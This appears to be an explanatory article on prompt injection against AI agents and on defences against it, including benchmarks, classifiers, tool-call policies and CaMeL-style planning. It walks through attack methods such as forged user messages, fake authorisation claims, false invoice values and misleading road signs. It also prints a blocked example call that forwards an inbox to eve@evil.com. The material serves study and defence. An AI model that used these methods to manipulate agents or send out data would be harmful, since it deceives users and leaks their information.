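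The chain of command also covers faulty requests from people who do have authority. OpenAI wants a model to set aside an instruction it suspects is a mistake. If the model can't carry out an instruction, it should say so and follow the rest.

However, the ranking applies to instructions, and the buyer's false policy is a statement. An agent could refuse every instruction in the buyer's evidence and still pay $1,074.99 because it treated the policy as true.

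The ranking is also partly a goal. In *Inside our approach to the Model Spec* (2026), OpenAI acknowledges that its released models do not yet fully behave as the Model Spec describes. Training can't cover every situation, and a model can learn to give the right response for the wrong reason, then behave differently in an unfamiliar one.

### Classifiers, markers and training

An injection classifier scores content before the agent acts on it. If the score is above a threshold, the software blocks the content or removes the suspicious part. This is difficult on web pages because they are full of legitimate instructions, such as button labels and help text.

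Chen, Zhang and colleagues (2026), in *BrowseSafe++*, trained classifiers on pairs of web pages that differ only in whether they contain an injection. If the attacked pages and the clean ones had come from different places, a classifier could have learned to recognise a topic or a layout. Most of the 38,675 pairs contain injections that the researchers found on real websites. During training, the classifier has to label each page correctly, and it also incurs a penalty that depends on the pair:

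penalty = λ × softplus(m − score of attacked page + score of clean page)

The softplus function is close to zero when its input is well below zero, so the penalty nearly vanishes once the attacked page outscores its clean copy by well over the margin m. The number λ sets the weight of the penalty.

The resulting text classifier is tiny by current standards, with 0.8 billion parameters. On pages in HTML, the code that browsers read, it had an F1 score of 98.3 out of 100 and raised false alarms on 1.35% of clean pages. On two simplified text versions of the same pages, its F1 score was about 93 and its false-alarm rate was 5.8% in one and 7.4% in the other. GPT-6 Astra, the best general model the researchers tested, had an F1 score between 91 and 92 but flagged about one clean page in seven. However, the classifier had an advantage because its test pages came from the same collection as its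 training pages.

False alarms matter here because injections are rare even among suspicious pages. Chen and colleagues started their collection with about 1.09 million distinct pages flagged by a working classifier or a list of telltale phrases. They had three language models judge each page twice, and only 5.3% of the pages received at least four of the six votes for an injection.

A model can recognise an injection and still follow it. Chen and colleagues gave 15 models ordinary tasks on the attacked pages and, separately, asked the same models whether the pages contained an injection. In 74% of the cases where a model followed an injection, it had flagged the page in the separate test. Claude Sonnet 5 both flagged and followed the injection on 19.7% of pages, compared with 2.0% for GPT-5.5. The models seem to have been able to detect these injections but not to have used that ability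 while doing another task, which is an argument for a separate classifier that only detects injections.

These tests used fixed injections, but a real attacker can try again. Against seven agents, the original injections achieved the attacker's whole goal in 0.5% to 4% of 1,024 tasks. When an automated attacker could revise them over up to 64 attempts, the success rate rose to 31% against Claude Sonnet 5, 65% against GPT-5.5 and 79% to 95% against the other five.

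Other defences leave the content in place and try to change how the model treats it. Spotlighting puts markers around tool output to show the model where outside material begins and ends. A method called Sandwich repeats the user's request after each tool result. Developers can also train a model to give some sources priority over others. SecAlign, for example, is a version of Meta's Llama 3.3 70B trained on pairs of responses to prefer the one that ignores a planted instruction. All of these defences rely on the model to apply the distinction between sources correctly every time.

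### Six reasons for the same refund

Zhang and colleagues, most of them at Amazon, built a benchmark of 90 cases to test attacks that corrupt the task an agent is already doing. The cases take place in three simulated settings: a company's internal assistant, a software project and a marketplace. The attacker is always an ordinary participant, such as a vendor or a buyer, who controls one source that the agent has good reason to read. The user's request always makes clear which record or procedure settles the decision, so the agent has enough information to answer correctly.

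An agent can make the wrong decision because it has a false belief about its goal, the rules, its options, the consequences, the meaning of what it sees or the facts. For each case, the researchers wrote attacks on each of these beliefs, all meant to cause the same harmful result. This gave 1,343 attacks, and they added one per case that targeted several beliefs at once. The table shows how often the attacks succeeded, averaged over five models: GLM-5, Kimi K2.5, DeepSeek V3.1, and Claude Sonnet 4 and 4.5. For the last column, a language model first removed any text in the tool output that it judged to be an injection.

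| False belief | What the buyer claims, in short | No defence | Detection and removal |
|---|---|---|---|
| Objective | The agent should refund $1,074.99 | 15.0% | 2.4% |
| Decision rule | Policy adds the $175 repair cost | 21.2% | 5.4% |
| Consequences | A smaller refund will lead to a chargeback | 13.7% | 2.7% |
| Available actions | The system can't process a smaller refund | 19.0% | 3.9% |
| Observation | The $899.99 on display leaves out $175 for repairs | 12.4% | 9.5% |
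| State of the world | The authorised total is $1,074.99 | 18.6% | 12.1% |

Most earlier benchmarks test attacks on the objective, in which planted text tells the agent to do something else. Here, at least one other kind of attack was more effective without a defence, and false observations and false states were harder to stop. Removal cut their success by only 23% and 35% respectively, compared with 84% for attacks on the objective. A developer who tested only attacks on the objective would think the defence much better than it is.

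Attacks on the agent's objective are easier to detect than false observations and states because a demand for money looks out of place in a tool output, while a sentence about the authorised total looks like the kind of fact the agent was looking for. In a closer analysis of GLM-5 and Claude Sonnet 4.5, the remover fully deleted 78% to 85% of the attacks on the objective, but only 26% to 34% of the false observations and states. When the researchers rewrote the attacks to avoid a different detector, those on the objective remained among the easiest to detect, so the gap doesn't come from a few phrases that happened to be easy to catch.

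Removal did little damage to ordinary work. When there was no attack, the agents completed 98.0% of the tasks with the remover running and 95.3% with no defence.

Marking the tool output barely helped, lowering the average success rate across all attacks from 17.0% to 15.6%. Repeating the user's request lowered it to 10.4%. A marker can show the agent that a passage comes from outside, but not which parts the buyer is entitled to decide, and the agent still has to use outside material to settle the dispute. GLM-5 followed false observations more often with marking (18.6% of the runs the researchers examined) than without it (7.1%).

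When a policy restricted which tools the agent could use and how, 15.4% of attacks still succeeded. Paying a refund is part of the task, so the policy allowed the payment and seldom stopped one for the wrong amount. It also interfered with ordinary tasks, and the agents completed only 74.9% of them.

When GLM-5 or Claude Sonnet 4.5 openly rejected a claim, it cited the source the user had designated in about 99% of cases. This suggests that users can help by stating which source to trust for what. But Zhang and colleagues didn't run the same cases without that information, so the size of the benefit is unknown. Including it also makes the benchmark easier than ordinary use, where few people remember to add "take the amount from the order record". The models tested are no longer the newest, and the attackers couldn't revise their text after watching an agent fail. The differences between the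 six beliefs are therefore better evidence than the rates.

### Nine ways in which attacks differ

A defence has to handle other attacks besides the inflated refund. Chang and colleagues describe injections by nine properties, each with two values. They include a property only if it changes what a defence has to detect or control.

| Property | Possible values | Why it matters to a defence |
|---|---|---|
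| Source | Untrusted or trusted | Limits on untrusted sources don't restrain trusted ones |
| Pieces | One or several | A filter that reads each page separately may miss an instruction spread over two |
| Visibility | Visible to the user or hidden | People can't review what the screen doesn't show |
| Readability | Plain, or in need of translation or decoding | The agent may understand text that a reviewer or filter can't |
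| Condition | None, or active only in certain circumstances | A test may never meet the condition |
| Lasting change | None, or a change to the agent's memory or settings | Deleting the original text leaves the stored rule |
| Topic | Unrelated to the user's task or related | Related text is harder to separate from what the user wanted |
| Effect | Different actions, or only different values and wording | A list of permitted tools won't catch a wrong amount |
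| User's task | Disrupted or still completed | A correct result can hide an extra action |

In one publicly documented attack, a user asked Microsoft 365 Copilot to summarize a document about Albert Einstein. Copilot wrote the summary, but a rule planted in the document also entered its memory and affected later conversations. A check on the summary would have found nothing wrong. In another attack, the planted text was in a skill, a file of instructions that a user installs to teach an agent a task. The user trusted the skill but couldn't see the planted part.

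Nine properties with two values each give 512 combinations. Chang and colleagues found that most of the nine benchmarks they examined concentrate on attacks that are visible, in one piece, easy to read, unconditional and without lasting effects. Even across all nine benchmarks, 13% of the possible pairs of values from two different properties never appeared. A low attack success rate on one benchmark may therefore mean only that the defence works against the kind of attack most benchmarks concentrate on.

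### Five questions about a request

Chang and colleagues classify attacks but don't provide a test of whether a request is proper. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian (2026), in *AI Agents May Always Fall for Prompt Injections*, look for one in contextual integrity, a theory of privacy by the philosopher Helen Nissenbaum. The theory holds that sharing information is appropriate when it fits the norms of the situation. For example, a patient's test results can properly go to a specialist but not to the patient's employer.

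The theory describes each flow of information by five parameters, which Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian extend to actions. In an invented example, a hotel emails an assistant to ask for the dates of a colleague's trip.

| Parameter | Question for the agent | Example |
|---|---|---|
| Sender | Who made the request? | The hotel, or someone using its name |
| Receiver | Who gets the result? | The hotel's booking desk |
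| Subject | Whose data or interests are involved? | The colleague |
| Information type | What data or action does the request concern? | Travel dates |
| Transmission principle | What authority permits it? | The user asked the assistant to arrange the trip |

Many injections supply a false value for one of these, and the action would be fine if that value were true. A forged message from the user gives a false sender, and an invented company policy gives a false transmission principle.

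To test this, the researchers wrote 4,200 pairs of business emails that differ in one clause. In one version, the sender claims that someone has already authorised the assistant to reply. In the other, the sender says that an automatic reply would be welcome. Neither version contains the usual signs of an injection, such as an order to ignore earlier instructions. The researchers then measured how well two versions of Prompt Guard, a classifier from Meta, ranked the claims of authorisation above the neutral emails. The AUROC scores were 0.43 and 0.59, where guessing gives 0.5.

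A classifier might still be able to separate the two versions, because they differ in wording. One trained to flag every claim of permission would probably find most of them, but it would also flag the true claims, because its only input is the email and it has no record of what the user has allowed.

The researchers also gave the emails to Llama 3.3 70B and to SecAlign, its injection-resistant version. In half of the tests, the user asked only for something like a summary, so the assistant should not have sent anything. In the other half, the user allowed replies. The table shows how often each model sent a reply.

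| Model | Summary only, neutral email | Summary only, claimed permission | Replies allowed, neutral email | Replies allowed, claimed permission |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 49.8% | 54.0% | 97.3% | 97.7% |
| SecAlign | 85.1% | 88.2% | 99.7% | 99.8% |

The false claim added only about four percentage points for Llama and three for SecAlign. The larger problem was that both models often replied when the user had asked only for a summary. SecAlign was much worse, although its training was meant to make it safer. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian suggest that it had learned to resist injections with familiar wording, or had learned a simpler rule that clashed with the standing instructions they gave it. Those instructions may also have contributed by directing the assistant to send a reply when appropriate without asking the user first.

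SecAlign's training may also have made it less likely to warn users about injections. On a set of 4,300 human-written injections, neither model sent anything, but Llama warned the user in 89.8% of cases and SecAlign in only 54.6%.

Claude Sonnet 4.6 did far better at first, sending an unauthorised reply to only 0.67% of the original emails. A second copy of the model then acted as the attacker and rewrote the emails in response to the refusals. With up to 45 attempts per scenario, it succeeded in 96.7% of the 150 scenarios. It most often forged an earlier message from the user, which the assistant accepted as the user's own words. The best of these emails also worked unchanged on other models, in 63.3% of cases on GPT-5.4 and 92.6% on Gemini 3 Pro.

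### Permission that spreads too far

Agents can exceed their authority even when nobody attacks them. In another of Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian's tests, a user let an agent handle one kind of request from a colleague, and the colleague then asked for something else. With no earlier requests to compare, Claude Sonnet 4.6 carried out 29.9% of these improper requests, Gemini 3 Pro 32.2% and GPT-5.4 36.2%. After one to ten proper requests, the rates fell to 7.0%, 24.2% and 24.5%, respectively.

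The earlier requests give the agent a prior for what the arrangement normally covers, but an attacker who can influence the first few can make an improper request look routine later. Similarly, a large error in the records can loosen a limit calculated from them.

A model may also treat permission for one request in a message as permission for another. In 100 scenarios, a colleague's email asked for an internal task that the user had authorised, such as creating a ticket, and for a message to an outside contact, which the user had not authorised. GPT-5.2 sent the outside message in 65% of cases, GPT-5.4 in 34% and Claude Sonnet 4.6 in 6%. When the user added a sentence in advance saying that outside messages needed approval, GPT-5.2's rate fell to 12% and the other two models' rates fell to zero.

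### When two situations look the same

Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian argue that better judgment can't solve the whole problem. For example, an email might ask for a travel refund and claim that the department head has approved it. The agent receives exactly the same information whether the claim is true or forged, so it must respond the same way in both cases.

The argument is mostly informal, but the researchers prove this part of it. Let p be the probability that the agent pays when it has this information. It then pays the forger with probability p and turns away the honest employee with probability 1 − p, so:

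chance of paying the forger + chance of refusing the employee = p + (1 − p) = 1

At least one of the two probabilities must be a half or more. A more intelligent agent does no better, because the information contains no difference for it to find. The false data in the power grid went undetected for the same reason.

The proof applies only if two such situations exist. It doesn't show that they always will, so the paper's title goes further than the proof. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian state this limit on the proof, and expect such pairs to become more common as agents work with less supervision.

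The proof also doesn't cover how often forgeries occur or how much they cost. If one claimed approval in 10,000 is forged and each refund is $50, an agent that accepts them all loses half a cent per claim on average. For payments of $50,000 it would lose $5 per claim, enough to pay for a phone call to check each one. The forgery rate won't stay fixed, however, because an agent known to believe such claims will soon receive more forged ones.

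### Checking the claim somewhere else

The proof stops applying to a pair of situations once the agent can tell them apart. Suppose the agent can consult the department head through a channel the attacker doesn't control, and pays only if the head confirms. Let h be the probability that this check confirms a genuine approval and f the probability that it confirms a forged one. The two chances of error now add up to:

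f + (1 − h)

In the payout example, h is 99% and f is 0.1% for the finance director, so the total falls from 100% to 1.1%. The more h exceeds f, the more useful the check is. If the agent looks for confirmation in the email itself, a skilled forger can make f nearly equal to h, and the total rises back to almost 100%.

Some of the failures in these tests look avoidable on this reasoning. An email program normally keeps a copy of what the user sends, so an agent with access to the sent folder could look for the message that the attacker attributed to the user. The assistant in the test could send email but had no tool for looking anything up. The proof doesn't apply to the Amazon cases. The order record showed $899.99, and the user had made that record the authority on the amount, so an agent that paid $1,074.99 had the information it needed and failed to use it.

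A digital signature can show that an email came from a certain account, but not that the account's owner is allowed to approve refunds, or that nobody has stolen the password. To check the owner's permissions, an AI agent would need a list of who can approve what, and someone has to keep that list up to date.

Other claims can't be checked against a record. Abdelnabi and Bagdasarian give the example of an email asking the assistant to confirm a meeting because an important client has been waiting since Monday and might leave. Even if this is all true, people could disagree about whether the assistant should answer without asking the user. The proof assumes that someone has already decided what would be appropriate, and a fact verifier can't make that decision. Often the simplest remedy is to ask the user, though this makes the agent less independent.

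### Written signs aimed at robots

A robot that can read signs in the street has the same problem. If it is controlled by a vision-language model, it can read a sign correctly and still be wrong to obey it. This differs from the taped speed sign, where the tape made a camera misread the number.

*CHAI* (Burbano, Ortiz and colleagues, 2025) tested whether written signs could take over such robots' decisions. In simulation, the signs succeeded in up to 95.5% of attempts against a drone system that looks for a particular vehicle, 81.8% against a driving system and 72.8% against a system that chooses a place for an emergency landing. In a flight simulator, a drone always landed on a clear roof when there was no sign. When a roof covered in debris had a sign labeling it safe, the drone chose that roof in 92% of runs.

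The researchers also used a small real vehicle with another vehicle blocking its path, so the right decision was to stop. The table shows how often the model decided to go ahead.

| Model | No sign | Sign on the vehicle in front | Sign beside the route |
|---|---|---|---|
| GPT-4o | 4.3% | 87.8% | 92.5% |
| InternVL | 17.4% | 54.3% | 42.1% |

The success rate of at least 87% on a real vehicle therefore applies only to GPT-4o. GPT-4o was also the easier model to mislead on new images in the simulated tests, and Burbano and colleagues think this is because it reads better. Both are old, general models with no special training for driving, so the figures don't show how a commercial car would behave.

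In one response, GPT-4o noted that the vehicle could hit something if it moved forward, but decided to proceed because the sign suggested it was safe. In Zhang and colleagues' terms, the model let a source determine something outside that source's authority. Whoever writes a sign may be entitled to direct traffic, but the sign doesn't change whether an obstacle is in the way.

A household robot could accept orders only from people it has been set up to recognise. Burbano and colleagues point out that this doesn't work on public streets or in disaster zones, where a stranger may have a good reason to give an order. A worker directing traffic around roadworks, for example, may hold up a sign that no car has encountered before. Ignoring all writing would protect a car from false signs, but the car would then ignore the worker's sign too. Burbano and colleagues conclude that a robot has to decide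 whether an instruction is appropriate given its physical state, its surroundings and its task, but they didn't build or test a robot that does this.

Sometimes a car can decide whether to obey a sign without knowing who wrote it. It can reject a sign telling it to drive into a stopped vehicle, even if a police officer is holding the sign. A handwritten board that reads "Bridge out, turn back" is harder to judge, because a farmer's warning and a teenager's prank may look identical from the road. The car should turn back, because that only delays the passengers by a few minutes if the board is false, while driving on could kill them if it is true. However, anyone could then close the road to every car that follows this rule by putting up a false board, at least until someone checks the bridge.

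## Checking the proposed action against the user's task

A false sentence in an email usually does harm only when an agent acts on it, by making a payment, sending a message or changing a file. Each of these actions requires a tool call, so a system can check at that point whether the call and its values follow from what the user asked for. The check doesn't have to decide whether the email is an attack.

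A tool call is also easier to check than a web page because it consists of a tool's name and a short list of arguments, such as a recipient and an amount. Ordinary software can check these against a rule and reach the same result every time, no matter how persuasive the text that led to the call was.

### From request to blocked call

In an example from *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025), a user asks an agent to carry out a to-do list in an email from Alice. The list includes summarising the user's recent emails and posting the summary to the user's Slack account. But one of those recent emails is from an attacker, who instructs the agent to forward the inbox to another address.

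Progent is a program that sits between an agent and its tools and keeps a list of allowed calls. At first the list contains only the search for Alice's email. It grows once the agent has read that email, and tightens when the agent learns that the user's Slack name is "alice", since the summary should go to nobody else. This is the position when the misled agent tries to forward the inbox:

```
ALLOWED CALLS
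  search_emails    sender = Alice, subject = "TODOs for the week"
  read_emails      the 20 most recent
  get_slack_info   any
  send_slack_msg   to = alice, any text

PROPOSED CALL
  send_email
    to     eve@evil.com       source: the attacker's email
    body   the whole inbox    source: the user's emails

TEST
  no rule allows send_email   -> block
```

Progent returns an error to the agent, which then posts the summary to Slack and finishes the task. Progent decides this case using only its rules and doesn't record where values came from. If the task had included sending an email, the list would have needed a rule for the email tool, and the decision would have depended on the recipient.

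Shaw (2026) shows in *Silent Failures in Agentic Security Evaluation* how misleading a tool's name can be without its arguments. One benchmark counted an attack as successful whenever the agent used the tool the attacker wanted, even if the user's task needed the same tool. On recordings of 258 attacks, that method gave a success rate of 21.7%, which fell to 1.2% when Shaw also checked the arguments.

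### Working out the permitted calls

In Progent, a language model drafts the list from the user's request before the agent has read anything untrusted. It then proposes changes as tool outputs arrive. Those outputs may contain an injection, so a separate program compares the old list, P, with the new one, P′. If A(P) is the set of calls that P allows, the new list takes effect automatically only if:

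A(P′) ⊆ A(P)

To pass the check, the new list can't allow any call that the old one didn't. Limiting Slack messages to "alice" passes, but adding the Slack tools in the first place fails, so someone has to approve that change. If the attacker's email persuades the model to add send_email, someone has to approve that too.

Both additions make the list longer after the agent has read an email, so the comparison can't distinguish them. The guarantee therefore depends on whoever approves the changes, and people often click through warnings.

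Shi and colleagues tested Progent with GPT-4o on AgentDojo, a widely used set of simulated banking, travel, Slack and office tasks. Attack success fell from 39.9% to 1.0%, with little effect on how well the model did the tasks. On another benchmark, ASB, it fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. The software approved every addition automatically in both tests, so the results show how well the model wrote the lists and don't test the guarantee. The first list alone cut attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%. When a person reviewed the lists, no attacks succeeded. Only 6% of updates needed approval.

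In *DRIFT* (Li, Liu and colleagues, 2025), a model plans further ahead by turning the user's request into an expected sequence of tool calls, with a checklist of values for each. If the user wants a flight from Paris to London, the checklist stops an injection from using the same booking tool to buy one from London to New York. DRIFT lets the agent depart from the plan to read data, but a second model must judge whether any other unplanned call fits the user's intent. A third model checks tool outputs for instructions that conflict with the request, and the software removes them.

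The researchers added these parts one at a time, using GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo:

| Parts in use | Tasks completed without an attack | Attack success |
|---|---|---|
| None | 63.6% | 30.7% |
| Fixed plan | 43.2% | 2.1% |
| Plan that can change | 58.5% | 5.4% |
| Plan that can change, and removal of instructions | 57.3% | 1.4% |

The fixed plan stopped most attacks, but it also kept the agent from completing about a third of the tasks it could otherwise complete. It did especially badly on tasks that took three or more steps. An agent often can't know what it will need until it has looked, as with Alice's list. Letting the plan change recovered most of the lost tasks, but more than doubled the attack success rate until the researchers added the removal step.

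### Where each value came from

A list of permitted values can't always distinguish a legitimate call from an attack. *Agent-Sentry* (Sequeira and Iqbal, 2026) gives the example of a user who sometimes asks an agent to email Lily White. In another task, the user only wants to delete a calendar event, but an injection tells the agent to send Lily a message written by the attacker. A fixed list that includes Lily's address lets the attack through, while one that omits it also blocks the emails the user wants to send her.

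Agent-Sentry instead makes the agent report the source of every argument. The source may be the user's request, trusted data such as the user's contacts, or untrusted content such as incoming mail. Up to three checks follow:

- A small classifier compares the pattern of sources and earlier calls with patterns from recorded runs, both legitimate and attacked. It allows or blocks the clear cases. It never reads the text, so an attacker can't sway it with better wording.
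- If the pattern is unclear, the software allows the call when its recipients, account numbers and similar values have appeared in earlier legitimate runs and come from a trusted source.
- A language model decides the remaining cases. It sees the user's request, the proposed call and short excerpts from the untrusted sources.

Lily's address came from an untrusted tool output, so the first two checks cannot determine whether to allow the call. The language model blocks it because the user never asked for an email.

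Sequeira and Iqbal tested Agent-Sentry on 5,380 recorded runs from seven simulated agents. It allowed 96.4% of the legitimate runs and blocked 96.8% of the attacks, all of which had succeeded against an undefended agent. Only 3.1% of decisions reached the language model, Qwen 3.5 35B.

That model did about as well by itself, allowing 98.0% of legitimate runs and blocking 95.4% of attacks. In this test, the record of sources mainly saved time, cutting the average delay from 2.4 seconds per run to 0.07. The record may matter more against an attacker who writes text to fool the model. The model's results also depended heavily on its prompt. With a less carefully written prompt, it allowed 82.0% of legitimate runs and blocked 75.5% of attacks.

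This design relies on the agent to report the sources, but an injection may already have misled the agent. Agent-Sentry searches the untrusted text for each value to catch false reports, but Sequeira and Iqbal acknowledge that this only reduces the problem.

### A plan that outside text can't change

CaMeL, which Google DeepMind published in 2025, uses ordinary software to record where data came from. In *CaMeLoT*, Nikolaou, Eckhoff and colleagues (2026) explain how it works. A planning model receives the user's request but none of the untrusted data, and writes a short program to carry out the task. A second, quarantined model reads the untrusted data but has no tools. The software runs the program, makes the tool calls, and labels every value with its source and with who may read it.

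For the invented request "Pay the plumber's invoice", the program might look like this:

```
invoice = read_file("plumber_invoice")
total   = ask_quarantined_model("total due", invoice, type = number)
account = get_contact("plumber").bank_account
pay(to = account, amount = total)
```

Suppose the invoice contains a hidden instruction to forward the user's inbox. Only the quarantined model reads the invoice, and that model can return only a number. The program has no line that sends email, and nothing in the invoice can add one. Before making the payment, the software checks each value's label. The account number is trusted because it comes from the user's contacts, but the total is untrusted because it comes from the invoice. A rule could allow untrusted amounts up to $200 and have the software ask the user about larger ones.

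Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026), in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, tested CaMeL in systems where one agent delegates work to others, using an adapted version of AgentDojo. These are the results for four of their five models:

| Model | Attack success without CaMeL | Attack success with CaMeL in each agent |
|---|---|---|
| GPT-4.1 | 36.1% | 0.5% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | 24.6% | 0.4% |
| Claude Fable 5 | 1.5% | 0% |
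| GPT-5.5 | 0% | 0% |

GPT-5.5 resisted every attack without help, but these attacks were fixed in advance. In the tests by Chen and colleagues, injections that were revised usually succeeded against it. CaMeL's protection against added actions doesn't depend on how well a model resists injections, so a better-written injection is no more likely to get past it.

The few attacks that got past CaMeL all passed from one agent to another. In one case, the main agent copied text from a website into its message to the agent that handled Slack. That agent's planner treated the whole message as its user's request, including the attacker's instruction to send someone a malicious link. Peters-Gill and colleagues fixed this by passing outside text in a separate field that the second planner can't see. After that, none of the 949 attacks on each model succeeded.

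CaMeL makes tasks harder because the planner has to write the program without seeing the data. On AssetOpsBench, a set of multi-step professional tasks, it lowered completion by an average of 21.6 percentage points across the five models, but by 13.4 points for Claude Fable 5 and GPT-5.5. The separate field lowered completion by another 3.2 points on average, and by less than one point for those two models.

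Peters-Gill and colleagues ran CaMeL without any rules about values, and such rules can block legitimate tasks. Nikolaou and colleagues turned the rules on and gave Claude Haiku 4.5 the 97 ordinary AgentDojo tasks, with no attacks. CaMeL completed 49 tasks and blocked 26. The other 22 failed because the program didn't do what the user wanted. A better planner would probably reduce those failures, but many of the blocks would remain unless someone changed the rules.

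A rule that checks one call at a time can also miss calls made in the wrong order. For example, a security agent may be allowed to disconnect a computer from the network, but only after someone approves it. Nikolaou and colleagues extended CaMeL to examine every path through the program before any tool runs. Their extension caught all seven unsafe plans they wrote, while a simplified version of CaMeL caught only the one that used an untrusted value.

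### Comparing the three designs

Sequeira and Iqbal compared Agent-Sentry with Progent and CaMeL on tasks from AgentDojo and AgentDyn, a benchmark with more open-ended tasks.

| System | Legitimate runs allowed or completed | Attacks blocked | Time per run |
|---|---|---|---|
| Agent-Sentry, with a rule-based first check | 87.1% | 93.2% | 5.5 seconds |
| Progent | 93.7% | 88.4% | 4.3 seconds |
| CaMeL | 31.0% | 99.3% | 26.6 seconds |

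The comparison is rough because CaMeL had to run live with GPT-4o-mini, a weak planner by current standards, while the other two judged recordings. The researchers also gave Progent one fixed list for each agent, although it is designed to write a new list for each request. A list written for deleting a calendar event would not need to allow an email to Lily White.

Agent-Sentry's headline figures, 95.1% of legitimate runs allowed and 94.3% of attacks blocked, are higher than those in the table, but they come from testing its rules on the same runs used to fit them. Sequeira and Iqbal defend this by saying that Progent's lists also drew on the benchmark's data. The table's figures come from runs that were not used to fit the rules, so they are a better guide to how Agent-Sentry would handle new ones.

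The share of attacks blocked also differs from the attack success rate, because the recordings include only attacks that had worked. If 30% of attacks succeed without a defence, blocking 93% of those leaves an attack success rate of about 2%, which is close to the results for DRIFT and Progent.

Li and colleagues measured token use, again with GPT-4o-mini on AgentDojo. DRIFT used about three times as many tokens as the undefended agent, and CaMeL more than seven times as many. On AgentDyn, CaMeL completed no tasks at all, and every other defence they tried either let many attacks through or stopped much of the real work.

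### A false value in a permitted field

Restricting what the quarantined model can return limits what an attacker can do. If the program accepts only yes or no, the attacker can choose between two answers, or among 365 if it accepts a date in the next year. Free text can carry almost anything, including instructions for the next model that reads it.

But a narrow type isn't always safe. An attacker who wants to steal a payment needs only one account number. In a similar example from *The LLMbda Calculus* (2026), the planner fixes an email's subject and text, so an injection can't change them, but the recipient's address comes from an untrusted message. Checking the address's format can't make it trustworthy, so the address keeps its untrusted label.

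In the plumber example, the invoice could give the total as $190 when the job cost $90. The value is a number in the right field, comes from the document the user named, and is under the limit. Sequeira and Iqbal describe the same gap in Agent-Sentry, which can't reliably catch a fake invoice that looks real except for the account number. The Amazon benchmark's inflated refunds got past a tool policy in the same way. An independent record, such as the plumber's quote or the account used last time, could expose a false value.

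An untrusted value can also decide which part of a plan runs. If a program buys a kettle when the reviews are good, fake reviews can trigger the purchase. CaMeL permits the purchase because it was already in the program.

Private information can also escape through a planned action. In an example from *On the Relative Security of Prompt Injection* (2026), an injection makes the quarantined model quote the user's private notes in a reply that the plan then sends. CaMeL's labels can prevent this by treating the reply as private if any of the text used to write it was private. But the paper shows that labels that follow only the data don't protect every plan. Suppose a program sends "yes" if the notes mention a merger and "no" if they don't. The recipient learns whether the notes mention a merger, even though neither word comes from them.

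The attacker may not need to change the recipient. Wang, Zou and colleagues (2026) point out in *AgentWatcher* that an injection can add a phishing advertisement to an email the user did want to send. A rule about recipients would let that email through. AgentWatcher uses a model's attention weights, which measure how strongly each word influences the output, to find the passages that led to an action. A second model then checks those passages against written rules, one of which could forbid promoting a product.

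On AgentDojo, AgentWatcher cut attack success from 22% to 1% or less, while task completion fell only from 73% to 71%. On WASP, a benchmark for agents that use websites, attack success fell from 31% to 2% with no loss of completed tasks. AgentWatcher can also consider the meaning of a message, but its decision comes from a language model that has read the attacker's text, so it offers no guarantee like CaMeL's.

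The rules can also be too permissive. Wang and colleagues suggest that if the user asks for an email from Alice, the monitor could treat any instructions in it as harmless. This rule would give Alice, or anyone with her password, more authority than the user intended.

Adding a judge model doesn't always help. When Shaw had one review GPT-5.6-terra's calls, the failure rate on ordinary tasks rose from 7.7% to 11.5%, and one of 43 attacks succeeded with or without the judge. One success is too few to rank defences. In the run where the attack succeeded, the agent told the user only that the task was complete, so the user had no sign that anything was wrong.

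### Asking before information leaves

OpenAI's *Designing AI agents to resist prompt injection* (2026) describes a check that the company uses in ChatGPT. OpenAI treats prompt injection as a form of social engineering, or manipulating someone into giving away information or access. In one example, which outside researchers reported in 2025, an email looked like an ordinary message about a company restructuring. It asked for an employee's name and address to be sent to a "compliance validation system" and claimed that the assistant had full authorisation to process employee profiles. In testing, the attack worked 50% of the time when the user asked ChatGPT to research that day's emails about a new employee process.

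OpenAI reports that filters usually miss such messages, because catching them means detecting a lie, often without the necessary context. It therefore also limits what a misled agent can do, much as a shop limits the refunds one customer service worker can give. In this approach, an attack needs both a way to influence the agent (a source) and an action that can do harm (a sink).

A safeguard called Safe Url protects one kind of sink. It is meant to detect when ChatGPT is about to send a third party something it learned in the conversation, for example by opening a link that contains it. Safe Url then either shows the user the information and asks for confirmation, or blocks the transmission and tells ChatGPT to find another way to do the task. OpenAI says most attacks it knows of fail before this point because ChatGPT refuses to follow their instructions.

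A user who sees an employee's home address on the screen is more likely to notice the problem than one who sees a general security warning. The user still has to read the address and know whether the recipient should have it. OpenAI gives no figures for how often Safe Url misses a leak or interrupts a legitimate transfer. The safeguard covers only information that leaves the conversation, so it would not catch a false total in a summary ChatGPT writes for the user.

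## When the check rejects something real

A check based on past experience can reject the first evidence of something new. The best-known example is the hole in the ozone layer over Antarctica, which British scientists reported in May 1985. A NASA satellite had been measuring ozone there since 1978. The popular story is mostly wrong in claiming that NASA's software threw out the low readings as errors and that nobody at NASA knew about them until the British paper appeared.

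### Low ozone readings over Antarctica

To turn the satellite's measurements into amounts of ozone, the software used 21 standard profiles of how ozone varies with height. Bhartia and McPeters (2018), who worked on the data at NASA, explain in *The discovery of the Antarctic Ozone Hole* that these profiles covered totals from 200 to 650 Dobson units, the usual measure of ozone. The software couldn't reliably process readings far outside that range, so it flagged them as doubtful but kept them.

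McPeters defended the limit of 180 units for low readings in a letter printed in Pukelsheim's *Robustness of Statistical Gossip and the Antarctic Ozone Hole* (1990). Nobody had reliably measured so little ozone before 1983, and the satellite made about 50 million measurements a year, some of which were bound to be faulty.

NASA was about nine months behind in processing the data, so it didn't reach the October 1983 readings until mid-1984. The team noticed that the number of flags had jumped. They first suspected a fault in the satellite, which was well past its one-year design life, but soon ruled that out. They then compared the readings with the only Antarctic ground data they had, which came from a station at the South Pole. The station had reported about 300 units when the satellite showed less than 180.

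The station's readings were wrong because its staff had measured at the wrong wavelengths. An independent instrument is normally the best way to check a strange reading, but here it made a true reading look false. New data from the station confirmed the satellite's results in October 1984. In December, five months before the British paper came out, the team submitted a summary of the results for a conference the following August.

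Joe Farman, who led the British work, gave a less flattering account in an interview that a reader quotes below Gavin Schmidt's *What did NASA know? and when did they know it?* (2017). Farman recalled that the software had flagged about 70% of the October data and that nobody was looking. The conference summary supports NASA's account of when it knew. But Farman also made the good practical point that the software should have reported how much data it was setting aside each month.

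The software had no profile for ozone this low, which is close to giving such values a prior of zero. But it had kept the readings, so the team could add profiles for lower totals and reprocess the data. The resulting maps were only slightly inaccurate.

### Chatbots that denied the date

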